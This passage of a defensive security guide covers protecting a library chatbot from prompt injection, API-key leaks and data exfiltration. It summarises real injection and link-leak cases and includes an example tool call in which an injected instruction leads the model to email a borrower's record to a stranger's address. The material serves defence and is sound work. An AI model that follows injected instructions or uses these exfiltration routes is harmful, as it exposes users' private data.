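The formula underestimates the risk when the attacker learns from failure. If the chance of success rose steadily from 1% on the first attempt to 3% on the hundredth, the chance of at least one success would be about 87%. The starting rate may also be too low if it was measured with weak attacks. The formula can also overestimate the risk, because an operator who reads the logs may notice the early failed attempts and block the page, which laboratory tests usually leave out. The 63% is therefore a rough guide to how quickly a small risk grows and shouldn't be used as a forecast.

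### Testing the library's chatbot

No system card covers the library's mix of tools, instructions and web pages, so the library should run its own test. The test needs a closed copy of the chatbot with the same model, system prompt and tool definitions, but with invented borrowers and an email tool that records messages instead of sending them. A programmer could build the test from scratch or add a library environment to AgentDojo, whose code is public.

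The provider runs web search and the library can't choose the results, so the test needs a stand-in tool. This tool can return saved pages, some with planted instructions. The test then leaves out any protection that the provider builds into its search, so the real chatbot may follow injected instructions somewhat less often. The pages with planted instructions should stay off the public web, where somebody else's chatbot could read them.

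Each planted instruction should ask for something harmless and easy to recognise, such as an email to a test address containing an invented marker word. If the model tries to send an email containing that word, it has followed the instruction. Other cases can ask for the marker in a search query. To test for leaks, staff can give an invented borrower a made-up phone number and check every outgoing API call for it.

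The log should record whether the model requested the call and whether the host application ran it. If the model asked to send 30 forbidden emails and the host application blocked them all, no harm would result, but the library would know that only the block had prevented it.

Ten borrower questions combined with four planted instructions make 40 cases. Running each case 25 times gives 1,000 attacks, and another 250 runs of the ten questions on clean pages measure normal completion. The Labor Day answer cost at least nine cents with GPT-6 Astra, so at that rate all 1,250 runs would cost at least $112. Some of the pages, both clean and planted, should contain legitimate instructions that the borrower needs, such as what to bring to a passport appointment.

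If none of the 1,000 attacks succeeds, the usual statistical rule puts the true rate below 0.3% with 95% confidence. But the rule assumes independent runs, and 25 runs of one case tend to turn out alike, so the library learns more by adding new cases than by adding runs. The 0.3% limit also applies only to attacks like those staff thought of, so a result of zero doesn't justify letting the email tool write to any address.

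The library should repeat the test whenever it changes the model, the system prompt or a tool definition, connects an MCP server, or lets a tool return a new kind of text. A monthly run would also catch unannounced changes by the provider. Staff should keep the old cases so that results stay comparable, and hide a few from whoever edits the system prompt, because a prompt adjusted until it passes known cases may do no better on new ones. A rise from 2 successful injections in 1,000 to 5 could easily be chance. If the number jumps to 20, the library should go back to the previous version while staff find out which cases changed.

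## Keeping API keys out of the model's reach

A chatbot could pass every test for injected instructions and still expose the library's API keys. An API key is a secret string that a program sends with each request to an outside service so the service can identify and bill the caller. Keys leak through web pages, shared files and error messages, often with no attacker involved and no fault in the model. The library can't prevent every leak, but it can build the host application so that the model never receives a key.

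### What a thief gains from a key

A key works for anyone who has it. Unless the library has restricted a key to certain network addresses, the service can't tell the library's server from a stranger's laptop. The library's chatbot needs three keys, and a thief could use each one differently.

| Key | Bills | Data | Actions in the library's name |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model provider | Model use, charged to the library | Any files or conversations the library stores with the provider | Few |
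| Email service | A charge per message | Often a list of sent messages and recipients | Fraudulent email from the library's own address |
| Borrower records | Usually none | Possibly every borrower's loans, fines and contact details | Possibly changes to records, such as cancelled fines |

At GPT-6 Astra's price of $10 per million input tokens, a thief who sent 50 million tokens an hour would cost the library $12,000 a day.

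The damage also depends on the permissions the owner gave the key. Amazon Web Services (AWS), which rents out servers and storage, lets customers create keys that can do only one job, but many customers use far more powerful ones. *Researchers found 768 leaked AWS keys that still work* (Constantin, 2026) reports that all 768 keys gave full control of the owner's account. Of these, 526 were root keys, which carry the account owner's powers.

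### Where keys end up

| Place | Leak without an attacker | Leak with an attacker |
|---|---|---|
| System prompt | The model quotes the key while explaining what it can do | A user, or text on a web page, gets the model to repeat it |
| Tool definition | The model copies the key into an argument, which ends up in a log | As with the system prompt |
| Browser or app code | A web archive copies the page | Anyone who opens the page's code can read the key |
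| Configuration file | A coding assistant reads the whole file to find one setting | Planted text leads the assistant to read the file and send the key out |
| Log | Staff send the log to a contractor | An intruder searches the logs for keys |
| Error message | A failed tool returns the full request, key included, and the model repeats it | A user causes errors until one of them contains a key |
| Connector settings | A developer publishes the settings file along with the code | Malware on the developer's computer copies the file |

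If an API key is in the system prompt, the model can reveal it, because it can repeat anything in its context. Telling the model to keep the key secret makes this less likely but doesn't rule it out, and the host application still sends the key to the model provider with every request. Developers may be tempted to put a key there because an instruction such as "use this key for the catalogue" works immediately.

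To avoid running a server, a developer may put the key in the web page and call the model's provider directly from the borrower's browser. *Keys on Doormats* (Durumeric, 2026) reports finding 1,748 exposed credentials for 14 providers, including cloud and payment services, in a search of 10 million websites. Many had been there for months or years. Of the credentials exposed in JavaScript, 62% appeared only in the files that developers' tools generate for publication. A scan of the original source code would miss those, so the library should search its finished site as well.

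An assistant with access to files can expose a key while trying to help. *'I leaked secrets': An AI agent confessed to its own data leak* (Udinmwen, November 2026) describes a coding assistant that couldn't find a configuration file during a routine code review. It instead read all the computer's environment variables, which are settings that an operating system passes to programs, and leaked live passwords. Over ten sessions, it had repeatedly read entire configuration files, exposing passwords for production systems and credentials for a personnel system. The case appears to come from NordLayer, which sells network security to businesses. A single case can't show how often this happens, but this leak happened without an attacker. Developers commonly store keys in environment variables to keep them out of published code, but an assistant that can read the variables can still expose them.

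### Two million planted secrets

Keys in prompts can also leak after they reach the companies that run the model. *Three breaches, endless leaks* (Moore, 2026) describes an experiment that measured such leaks. HD Moore is chief research officer at Dragos, which sells security for industrial systems such as power grids and factories. From July to November 2026, Moore's team sent about two million prompts to widely used AI services. Each prompt contained unique web links and credentials, such as working AWS keys for empty accounts. Each link or credential appeared in only one request, so any attempt to use it showed that someone had read that request.

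The team found attackers stealing data from three companies that host models, none of which knew until Dragos told them. In the largest theft, in late October, the attackers took every request that Dragos sent to one provider during a few short periods. Those requests contained a couple of hundred AWS keys. The attackers tested some keys within hours, looked for more credentials, and tried to add their own users to the accounts. Constantin (2026) reports in *Dragos planted 2m secrets in AI prompts and caught 3 hacked providers* that the stolen keys led to tens of thousands of calls to AWS.

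Some of the requests taken in the other two thefts had a "zero data retention" setting, which is supposed to prevent the provider from storing them. According to KBY Technologies' *Dragos Canary Prompts Found Theft at Three AI Providers*, some of the keys stolen in October came from requests that the provider had rejected before any model ran. Dragos concluded that the attacker was copying requests as they arrived. If so, no storage setting could have protected those requests.

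Other secrets leaked without a break-in. On a marketplace where sellers compete to run models at the lowest price, some sellers recorded customers' prompts and tried the passwords in them by hand. A Chinese AI lab, which Dragos didn't name, opened the links from more than half of the prompts sent to its models. KBY Technologies reports that someone posted one of these links in a workplace chat 24 days after Dragos sent it, and that people opened it from six devices in Beijing and Shanghai.

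Many of the requests passed through several companies. OpenRouter, for example, forwards customers' requests to other companies that run the models. In *Data Processing Incidents on Inference Providers* (2026), OpenRouter announced that it had dropped three providers and withdrawn the zero-retention label from 125 endpoints, the addresses at which providers offer particular models. It said the findings showed no breach of its own systems. *Data processing incidents at the inference providers behind OpenRouter* (2026) describes a notice from the model developer MiniMax, which said its security monitoring had extracted web addresses from some requests and automatically opened some of them. MiniMax said it had turned this off on the routes it had confirmed and had found no sign that prompts or responses had reached outsiders.

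The experiment is strong evidence that strangers read some prompts, because the use of a unique key is hard to explain any other way. It doesn't show what share of all prompts leak, because Dragos chose which services to test and the largest theft came from a few short periods at one provider. The library rents its model directly from the developer, which Dragos considers the least exposed arrangement. A provider can still suffer a breach, but a key that isn't in the prompt can't leak this way.

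### How many keys leak in public code

Most counts of leaked keys come from companies that sell tools for finding them. One of these companies, GitGuardian, scans public code on GitHub. Its report *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* counted 1,275,105 leaked secrets for AI services in 2025, 81% more than in 2024. These included 113,000 API keys for the Chinese developer DeepSeek. Part of the rise came from a 43% increase in the number of commits (saved changes to code). Leaks of AI secrets per commit rose by about 27%.

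SC Media's *AI coding assistants twice as likely to leak secrets* puts GitGuardian's count of leaks of all kinds at about 28.65 million, up 34% from the year before, but the number of leaks per commit fell slightly. Relative to the amount of code, the growing problem is therefore leaks of AI keys in particular.

A daily.dev summary of the same research reports 24,008 secrets in MCP configuration files. It also reports that 3.2% of commits made with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding assistant, leaked a secret, compared with 1.5% of commits in general. The assistant didn't necessarily cause the extra leaks, since its users may have less experience or build more projects that need keys.

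Many leaked keys keep working for years. Truffle Security, which also sells secret scanning, searched a snapshot of 224 million public GitHub repositories (project folders) and tested the credentials it found in July 2026. Its *GitHub Repos Exposed 543,699 Credentials. Nobody Revoked Them* (2026) reports that half of the working credentials had been public for at least 784 days and that the oldest dated from 2009. Both companies benefit from alarming numbers, but Truffle's figure is harder to dismiss because it includes only credentials that the services still accepted.

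GitHub blocks developers from publishing credentials in formats it recognises. Truffle found that this roughly halved the rate at which such credentials reached public code, but 51.8% of the working credentials were in formats GitHub doesn't recognise. Jungco (2026) reports in *26,400 Valid Cloud and AI Keys Exposed on Gitee* that working keys also appear in public code on a Chinese hosting site.

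### Adding the key after the model has finished

The main rule is that the model names the tool and its arguments, and other software adds the key afterwards. When a borrower asks for a reminder by email, the model writes:

```json
{
  "id": "call_3",
  "tool": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "borrower@example.org",
    "subject": "Your library loan",
    "text": "Your book is due on Monday 14 December."
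  }
}
```

The host application reads this request, checks it, and fetches the email key from a secret store, a service that holds credentials and records which programs fetch them. It then sends the email service a new request, simplified here:

```
POST /messages
Authorization: (email key, added by the host application)

to: borrower@example.org
subject: Your library loan
text: Your book is due on Monday 14 December.
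```

Finally, it adds a short result to the model's context:

```json
{ "id": "call_3", "result": "Email accepted for delivery" }
```

The key appears only in the second step, which the model never reads. The key could still reach the model through the result if a carelessly written host application returns the email service's whole response, including any error that repeats the original request. It is safer for the library to return its own short message and keep the details in a log, with the key removed.

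A proxy, a separate program that receives requests and forwards them, can add the key instead. This is useful when a model writes and runs its own code, as coding assistants do, because the code can send its requests to the proxy and the computer running it needs no real key. The proxy must add each key only to requests for the service that issued it. Otherwise, an injected instruction could make the code send a request to an attacker's server, and the proxy would add the key.

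If the model's provider runs the connector to an MCP server, the library has to give the provider a credential for that server. The library should put the credential in the field meant for it, never in the prompt, and the credential should have as few permissions as possible.

Keeping the key out of the context stops the model from disclosing it, even if a borrower's message or a web page contains instructions to do so. The model can still misuse the tool. If an injected instruction makes the model request an email to a stranger, the host application will add the key and send the email unless another rule blocks the call. Without the key, though, the attacker can misuse the email service only through the chatbot, and can't bypass the library's checks by using the service directly. A break-in at the host application or the secret store would still expose the keys.

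### Shared keys, keys per user and temporary access

The library must also decide whose access the chatbot uses. The choice matters little for the email service, which belongs to the whole library, but a great deal for borrower records.

| Arrangement | What a stolen credential opens | What the log shows | How long the credential works |
|---|---|---|---|
| One shared key | Every borrower's record | Only that the chatbot made the request | Until the library revokes it |
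| One key per borrower | One borrower's record | Which borrower's key the chatbot used | Until the library revokes it |
| Temporary access through OAuth | The parts of one record that the borrower approved | The borrower and the application | Often about an hour |

A shared key is easy to set up, but one leak exposes everyone. Separate keys limit the damage from a single leak and make the log more useful. However, the library has to create, store and revoke thousands of keys, and a thief who broke into the key storage could take them all.

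OAuth is a standard that lets a person give a program limited access to an account without sharing the password. The chatbot sends the borrower to the record system's own login page, which lists the access the chatbot requests, such as reading loans but not changing the address. If the borrower agrees, the record system issues the host application a temporary credential with only those permissions. This credential is called an access token and is unrelated to the tokens that a model reads. The host application adds it to requests as it would an API key.

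A stolen credential is less useful if it expires quickly. One that lasts an hour would be useless after the 784 days in Truffle's figure, and probably by the time some of the thieves in Moore's experiment tried their keys, but a fast thief could still use it. Many systems also issue a second, longer-lived credential, which the host application exchanges for new temporary ones so the borrower doesn't have to log in every hour. The library has to protect this second credential as carefully as an API key.

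MCP makes authorisation optional. Since 2025, the specification has based authorisation on OAuth 2.1 for servers that require it and that clients reach over the web. The client must name the server it wants a credential for, and the server must refuse credentials meant for any other. A server that needs data from another service must get a separate credential for that service instead of forwarding the client's. The client must send its credential in the request's header, never in the web address, which logs often record. The specification recommends short-lived credentials but doesn't require them.

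These rules don't cover MCP servers that run on the user's computer and exchange messages directly with the host application. Under the specification, those servers should take credentials from their environment. A coding assistant on the same computer may be able to read those credentials, as in the November case, so a developer should keep the assistant and the server in separate environments.

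### A chatbot with staff access

Even when its keys are well protected, a chatbot can act as a confused deputy and show a borrower someone else's record. For example, the vendor of the library's record system might offer only staff keys, which can open any record. If a programmer then adds a card-number field to the account lookup so that parents can check their children's loans, a borrower could give the chatbot another person's card number and see that person's record.

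A borrower then types a neighbour's card number and says the neighbour needs help with a fine. The model accepts the explanation and requests the lookup. The host application adds the staff key, and because the key is valid, the record system returns the neighbour's loans and address. The borrower has obtained information that the record system would not have returned to a borrower's login, even though the key hasn't leaked and the model hasn't received instructions from a web page.

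The library's original design avoids this by taking the card number from the borrower's login. That works as long as every programmer who changes the lookup or adds a similar tool does the same. OAuth adds a second safeguard, because the record system rejects a request for the neighbour's record made with this borrower's credential, even if the story led the model to send it.

If the supplier doesn't support OAuth, the library can put a small program in front of the record system. The program holds the staff key, takes the borrower's identity from the login session, and returns only that borrower's record. Parents can still see their children's loans if staff link the accounts in advance and the program checks for that link. If the model had to judge whether someone is a parent, a user could lie to it and get another borrower's record.

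### Spending limits and responding to a leak

A spending limit on each key limits how much of the library's money a thief can spend before anyone notices. With GPT-6 Astra, searching and reading the results for the library's 200 questions a day costs about $13. Reading the 3,000-token context three times for each question would add $18. A limit of $60 a day would leave room for busy days, and a thief could spend at most $420 in a week.

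Some services only send a warning when spending passes the limit, or calculate spending with a delay, so the library should check that its limit stops requests. With a hard limit, a thief or a burst of unusually long questions can shut the chatbot down for the rest of the day. Separate keys for testing and the public chatbot prevent a mistake in one from stopping the other. For the email key, a limit on the number of messages matters more than one on cost, because a few dollars can pay for thousands of fraudulent emails.

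If a key may have leaked, the library should act in this order:

1. Revoke the key. The tool that uses it will stop working until the next step, which is usually better than leaving the key active while staff investigate. Deleting the file or message that contained it isn't enough, because others may already have copies. Ayrey (2026), in *Scanning 7.6 Petabytes of HuggingFace Training Data for Secrets*, found 221,303 working credentials in public collections of AI training data.
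2. Replace it with a new key that has only the permissions the tool needs, and put the new key in the secret store.
3. Read the service's usage log from the earliest date on which the key could have leaked. Staff should look for unfamiliar addresses, unusual hours and sudden increases in use. They should also look for new users and keys, because the thieves in Moore's experiment tried to create their own users, and such accounts can keep working after the library revokes the original key. If someone read borrowers' records, the library may have a legal duty to tell them.
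4. Find out how the key leaked. Staff can search the code, the published website, logs and saved prompts for the old key. If they don't close the gap, the new key may leak the same way.

The library doesn't need proof of theft before it replaces a key. *Data processing incidents at the inference providers behind OpenRouter* reports that Atlas Cloud, which resells MiniMax's models, advised customers to treat any secret they had sent to three of those models as exposed. *Dragos Canary Study* (McDaniel, 2026) likewise recommends replacing any credential that someone may have pasted into a prompt. McDaniel works for GitGuardian, which sells a product to block such pasting, but replacing a key is a small inconvenience compared with the damage a stolen one could do.

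Dragos also recommends that developers plant fake credentials. The library could put a fake key in its system prompt that gives access to nothing and triggers an alert when anyone tries to use it. An alert would show that someone had read the prompt, and staff could start looking for the leak. The lack of an alert would be much weaker evidence that nobody had read it, because a thief might read the prompt for borrowers' data and never try the key.

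## Limiting which calls can run and where data can go

An injected instruction can make the model request a harmful call even when the API keys are out of its reach, but ordinary code in the host application can refuse to run that call. For example, a check that allows email to only two recipients works the same way whether or not an injected instruction has misled the model. Such limits restrict what a misled model can do, but they can't make the chatbot's answers true.

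OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) compares a chatbot to a customer-service worker who can grant refunds. Some customers will deceive the worker, so the company's software limits refunds no matter what the worker believes. OpenAI advises operators to place the same controls on a chatbot that they should place on a person in its position.

### Fewer tools and fewer permissions

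OWASP, an open community that publishes security guidance for software developers, uses the term "excessive agency" for the flaw that lets a model's bad output cause damage. Its *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* gives three common causes. The model may have tools it doesn't need, the tools may have permissions they don't need, or a high-impact action may go ahead without an independent check. Fixing these problems also helps when there is no attacker, because a model can make a damaging call by mistake.

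OWASP's example is an assistant that summarises incoming email. Its developer chose a connector that can also send messages, so an instruction planted in an email could make the assistant forward private mail to an attacker. The developer could reduce this risk by using a connector that only reads mail, logging in to the mail service with read-only permission, or requiring the user to press "send". The first two remove the assistant's ability to send anything, while the third works only if the user reads the draft.

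OWASP (2026) weighed experts' opinions against thousands of real incidents to compile its latest list of the ten main risks to applications built on language models. Excessive agency rose from sixth to third, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*.

The library's chatbot has no unused tools yet, but it could easily end up with some. A tool that staff tried and replaced may stay on the list by accident. An MCP server can gain a new tool in an update, and a read-only connector may gain write access. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) recommends keeping such additions switched off until the person responsible has reviewed them. The host application should therefore keep its own allow list of tool names instead of offering the model everything a server lists.

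The account lookup only needs to read, and the record system is the best place to enforce this, because the limit then holds even if the host application has a bug. The record system can give the lookup a credential that can view loans but not change them. The lookup can also return less data, since an injected instruction can't extract data that never enters the context. To answer questions, the model needs a borrower's loans and fines but not the phone number or home address, and the host application can find the email address itself when it sends a message.

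### The Rule of Two

Tools that are safe separately can be dangerous together. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) offers a simple test for combinations, partly inspired by Willison's three conditions for data theft. Within one session, a model should have no more than two of these properties:

- **A:** It processes untrusted text.
- **B:** It has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** It can change something or communicate with the outside world.

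A task that needs all three should continue in a new session with an empty context, or run with supervision, such as having a person approve its actions. Meta intends the rule to apply until models can reliably detect and refuse injected instructions.

Meta applies the rule to an email assistant in three ways. The assistant could read mail only from trusted senders, which removes A. It could work in a test environment with no private data, which removes B. Or it could send mail only to trusted recipients or after a person has checked the draft, which restricts C.

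Property C is broader than Willison's third condition because it includes changes such as deleting a file. The rule still permits A together with C, so it would allow a chatbot with only search and email, which could send fraudulent messages. The library could count its mail account as a sensitive system, but Meta's definition leaves this unclear. Meta describes the rule as a supplement to least privilege, the principle that each component gets only the access its task needs, and lists spam among the problems the rule doesn't solve.

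The library's original chatbot had all three properties. Meta allows a session to switch from one pair to another, for example by giving up outside communication before it accesses internal systems. The library can do something similar because every request to the model includes the tool definitions. Once the account lookup has returned a record, the host application omits the web search and page-opening tools from all later requests in that conversation, because it can't inspect provider-run searches in advance. If the model requests a search and the lookup in the same output, the host application refuses the lookup until the search has finished.

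This makes the chatbot less convenient, because a borrower who has asked about fines must start a new chat before asking about passport fees. Changing the tool definitions also means the next request doesn't get the provider's discount for stored text, which adds a few cents with GPT-6 Astra.

### Checking arguments and recipients

The library's original email tool accepted any text and any address. A narrower definition removes most of that freedom:

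```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "description": "Emails the borrower a list of current loans and fines, or passes a question to the front desk.",
  "arguments": {
    "recipient": "borrower or front_desk",
    "question": "up to 500 characters, for the front desk only"
  }
}
```

The host application replaces "borrower" with the email address on the logged-in account and "front_desk" with the library's own address, and it refuses any other value. The code has to check the value every time because the model may still write something else in the field despite the schema.

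The host application also writes the text of messages to borrowers, using the account data. If the model wrote this text, an injected instruction could make the library email its borrowers a false demand for payment. The front desk receives questions as plain text without clickable links.

Checks on a call's arguments can miss that its purpose is outside the agent's task. In an example from OpenAI, an agent that processes invoices finds that a document-signing subscription is about to lapse and tries to renew it. The vendor and the amount may be within the agent's limits, but renewing commits the company to a contract, which is not part of the agent's task. OpenAI recommends a separate approval for new commitments. The library avoids most such cases because none of its tools can pay, sign or cancel anything.

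### How a web address carries data out

An allow list of websites works much like a list of recipients, but page requests are harder to control than emails because the address can carry data to the site. In an example from OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links*, ChatGPT has information that a user lives in London and offers a link to a car-search site with "London" at the end of the address. Opening the link sends that information to the site.

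The user in that example probably wants the site to know, but an attacker could use an injected instruction to get a borrower's loans by the same route.

Anthropic restricts its page-fetching tool to addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, whether in the user's message, a search result or the result of an operator-run tool. The tool rejects any address the model composes itself, so the model can't attach a borrower's data to an existing address.

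OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains a different rule, used for ChatGPT. A crawler, a program that scans public web pages, builds an index of addresses without access to any user's conversations. ChatGPT can open a link automatically if its exact address is in the index, because an address that was public independently of the conversation is much less likely to contain the user's data. Otherwise, ChatGPT either looks for another site or warns the user that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation. For sites that opt out of being catalogued by OpenAI, ChatGPT asks the user to confirm every link.

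| | Anthropic's page-fetching tool | OpenAI's rule for ChatGPT |
|---|---|---|
| Opens an address automatically if | It has appeared in the conversation | The exact address is in the independent index |
| Otherwise | Returns an error | Tries another site or warns the user |
| A closure notice posted an hour ago | Opens if the search found it | Probably needs the user's approval until the crawler has found it |
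| Main weakness | Untrusted text can supply an address | The user may approve the warning without reading it |

When Anthropic released the tool in September 2025, Willison pointed out that many applications paste untrusted text into the user's message, and that the results of operator-run tools can also contain it. The library has this problem on a small scale. If a self-published e-book had a web address in its title, the account lookup would bring that address into the conversation, and Anthropic's rule would then allow the model to open it. Removing the page-opening tool after the lookup prevents this.

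Anthropic's rule also had an exception for links inside pages that the tool had already fetched. In July, Willison (2026) reported in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* that the researcher Ayush Paul had demonstrated how this exception could leak a user's name, home city and employer from Claude's chat app. Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and it removed the exception.

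The fix may not cover operators who use the tool through the API. The Japanese edition of Anthropic's *web fetch tool*, from August 2026, still lists links from earlier fetched pages as permitted, though the translation may be out of date. The library can check by asking the model to follow a link between two of the library's own harmless pages. Either way, Anthropic advises against using the tool where a model handles untrusted text alongside sensitive data.

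### Weaknesses in lists of trusted sites

A simpler rule would let the model open only well-known sites. OpenAI says this helps but gives two reasons not to rely on it. Many legitimate sites can redirect a visitor elsewhere, so a request that starts at a trusted site may end at an attacker's. A strict list also blocks many harmless pages, and users who see frequent warnings about them may learn to approve everything.

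A listed site may also let anyone store data there. The email app Superhuman allowed images from a Google domain that also hosts online forms, and anyone can create a form that keeps what it receives. Willison describes researchers showing that private emails could leak this way, and Superhuman fixed the flaw. *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) describes a similar weakness in an Anthropic product. Its list of permitted destinations included a service where any customer could store files, so data could end up in a stranger's account.

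Lists also become outdated. Salesforce, which sells customer-management software, still trusted a domain whose registration had expired. Researchers registered the domain and showed that it could receive customer data. Salesforce then corrected the list and stopped its agent from producing links to untrusted sites.

The library can use a much shorter list of allowed sites than ChatGPT could, because answering borrowers' questions about fees and opening hours requires few sites. It could let the model open pages only on the library's site and the State Department's, and have the tool refuse everything else without asking the borrower. Staff should review the list regularly. In Anthropic's filter, listing a domain also permits all its subdomains, and Anthropic warns that a letter from another alphabet can make a false domain look identical to a real one.

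The chat window needs its own rule because it is the library's code, and Anthropic's tool doesn't control what it displays. The library can limit clickable links to those that lead to its own site or exactly match a citation returned by the search. This keeps search citations clickable, as OpenAI's terms require. The window then shows any other address as plain text and loads no images from outside.

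### Call caps, isolation and outgoing traffic

The library could allow three searches and two opened pages per question, two emails per conversation, and eight passes through the tool-call loop. At GPT-6 Astra's price, reading the 3,000-token context eight times costs about 24 cents, and reading tool results adds to that. Anthropic's page-fetching tool has no cap unless the operator sets one.

An attacker who can log in could avoid the caps on each conversation by starting new ones, so the library also needs daily caps for each borrower and for the whole chatbot. The spending limits on the library's API keys remain as a last resort. OWASP lists caps among the measures that reduce damage but don't prevent it. For example, if the email tool still accepted any address, a single message could send a borrower's whole record to an attacker.

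Some chatbots also write and run code. The library's doesn't, but staff might later want it to analyse a spreadsheet of visitor numbers. Such code should run in a sandbox, an isolated environment with no access to the library's other files, programs or network. Otherwise, it could open its own connection to the internet and bypass every check on the email tool. OpenAI points out that the software that runs the tool-call loop doesn't provide this isolation by itself.

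Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* notes that developers have to configure a sandbox for each new capability, and that any task needing network access breaks the isolation. A compromise is to allow access to only a few sites. Codex, OpenAI's coding assistant, has settings for which sites the code may contact and which types of request it may make. Limiting the code to requests that only retrieve pages can still let data out, because the address can carry it.

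The library can apply the same idea to the server that runs the host application. A firewall can restrict the server's outgoing traffic to the model's provider, the email service and the record system. If a programmer later adds a carelessly written tool, the server still can't contact a site that isn't on that list. The firewall doesn't affect searches run by the provider, because they leave from the provider's machines. It also can't distinguish the library's account with the email service from an attacker's, so the host application or a proxy should add the library's own key and discard any other key.

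### Lockdown Mode in ChatGPT

Lockdown Mode is an optional ChatGPT setting that blocks many of the ways data can leave. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it in February for organisations in business, education and healthcare, and OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts in June.

With the setting on, ChatGPT browses only stored copies of web pages, so browsing sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network. It also stops retrieving images from the web and downloading files. The setting turns off agent mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on websites, and deep research, which produces long reports from many sources. Code in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing workspace, can't connect to the network. On personal accounts, the setting also blocks live access to connected services, or changes made through them, when either conflicts with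 its protections.

Users can still upload files, generate images, share conversations and use ChatGPT's memory of earlier chats. The setting doesn't affect Codex's network access. An instruction planted in an uploaded file or a stored web page can still change an answer. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* says data could still leak through connected apps, new techniques or unforeseen combinations of features.

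Lockdown Mode makes ChatGPT much less useful for current information. Search results may be old or missing, and shopping agents and ChatGPT's finance features don't work. The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* concludes that ChatGPT loses most of what makes its agent and research features useful, but considers this worthwhile for anyone handling sensitive data. OpenAI says most users don't need the setting. Users can turn it off for a single chat, which is convenient but makes it easy to give up the protection when it gets in the way of a task.

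In organisations that manage their own workspace, administrators choose which apps remain available. OpenAI advises against any use of untrusted apps, and against letting even a trusted app make changes that an outsider could see. By this standard, adding an entry to a public events calendar is as risky as sending an email, since anyone can read the entry. OpenAI rates reading from a trusted app as a medium risk, because the app can supply private data even though it can't send any.

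Library staff who use ChatGPT with borrowers' data could turn on Lockdown Mode. The library has to build equivalent limits into its own chatbot.

### When to ask a person

A person's approval is most useful for calls that are hard to reverse, cost money or affect someone outside the conversation. OpenAI's examples are sending funds, changing records and contacting customers. Asking borrowers to approve every search would only annoy them, and most of them couldn't judge whether the search words were safe.

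The request for approval should show what the call will do, what it will affect, and where any data will go. A borrower can check "Send this question to the front desk?" when it is followed by the full text, but "Allow the chatbot to use email?" leaves out both the recipient and the message. The host application should build the request from the call's actual arguments, because an injected instruction could influence a summary written by the model.

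People may not pay much attention to even a clear permission request. Claude Code traditionally asked developers before running a command or changing a file, and they approved 97% of these requests, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). They weren't necessarily careless, since most of the commands were probably safe.

Better evidence comes from an experiment in which Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study without telling them which behaviour it was measuring. Partway through each session, one approval request contained a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. About 17% of testers who saw the command early in a session refused it, compared with about 5% of those who had already answered 50 or more requests.

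The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than a real developer and may have paid less attention. Anthropic was also using the results to justify replacing most approval requests with an automated check. Still, approving out of habit would explain the drop during long sessions.

Developers rejected 39% of the plans that Claude Code presented for approval, but only 3% of requests for single actions. People may look harder at plans because they come up less often and describe the whole task. They may also reject a plan because they prefer another approach, so the 39% rate is weak evidence of how well they notice danger.

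One way to address habitual approval is to ask users less often. In Claude Code's newer "auto mode", the model can read files without approval. It can also edit project files, because developers can review and undo those edits. Another model checks most other actions, including shell commands and web requests. If it blocks three actions in a row, or 20 in a session, the software goes back to asking the user.

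The automated check blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands in the experiment, or 89%. The testers caught only six that it missed, so combining the two would have raised the total to 943.

An earlier test used 52 real cases in which Claude had tried to do more than the user wanted. The check missed about nine of them (17%), though with so few cases the true miss rate could be quite different. It also wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary calls. Anthropic says the check usually detected the danger in the missed cases but was wrong about whether the user had agreed to the action. Anthropic doesn't consider the check a replacement for careful human review of high-stakes systems.

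In an outside test that Anthropic commissioned, none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. Only 0.09% of attempts succeeded against Claude models without auto mode's check, so the result mostly reflects the models' own resistance and is weak evidence of how well the check works.

The automated check is a model, so it can fail in ways that a fixed list of recipients can't. OpenAI says advisory checks should never be the only protection against an action that must not happen automatically. For a small chatbot like the library's, removing dangerous options is cheaper and more reliable than having a person or a second model judge each call. Only messages to the front desk need approval, because they contain text written by the model. They are also rare enough that borrowers may read them.

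### The library's finished permissions

| Tool or output | What the model controls | What it can reach | Limits in code | Approval |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clock | Nothing | The library's date and time | Read-only | None |
| Web search | Search words | The public web, through the provider | Three per question, none after an account lookup | None |
| Page opening | An address already in the conversation | The library's and State Department's sites | Two per question, none after an account lookup | None |
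| Account lookup | Nothing | The logged-in borrower's loans and fines | Read-only, no contact details | None |
| Email | A choice of two recipients, and the text of a question to staff | The borrower's own address and the front desk | Two per conversation, text for borrowers written by code | Borrower confirms messages to the front desk |
| Links and images in answers | The text of the answer | The library's site and exact search citations | Other addresses not clickable, no outside images | None |

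Suppose a borrower asks on Thursday 10 December 2026, "Do I owe anything, and is there a book sale this weekend?" The model searches for the sale and finds a local events page that gives the date but also contains an injected instruction. The model then requests the account lookup. The host application returns a record of a $2.40 fine and a list of loans, and leaves the search and page-opening tools out of its next request to the model.

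The model follows the injected instruction and asks to send the record to an outside address:

```json
{
  "id": "call_4",
  "tool": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "recipient": "stranger@example.net",
    "question": "(the borrower's loans and fines)"
  }
}
```

The host application first confirms that `send_email` is on its list of tools and that the conversation hasn't reached its email cap. It then compares the recipient with the two permitted values and finds no match. It never fetches the email key or contacts the email service. The model receives a short result:

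```json
{ "id": "call_4", "result": "Refused: recipient must be borrower or front_desk" }
```

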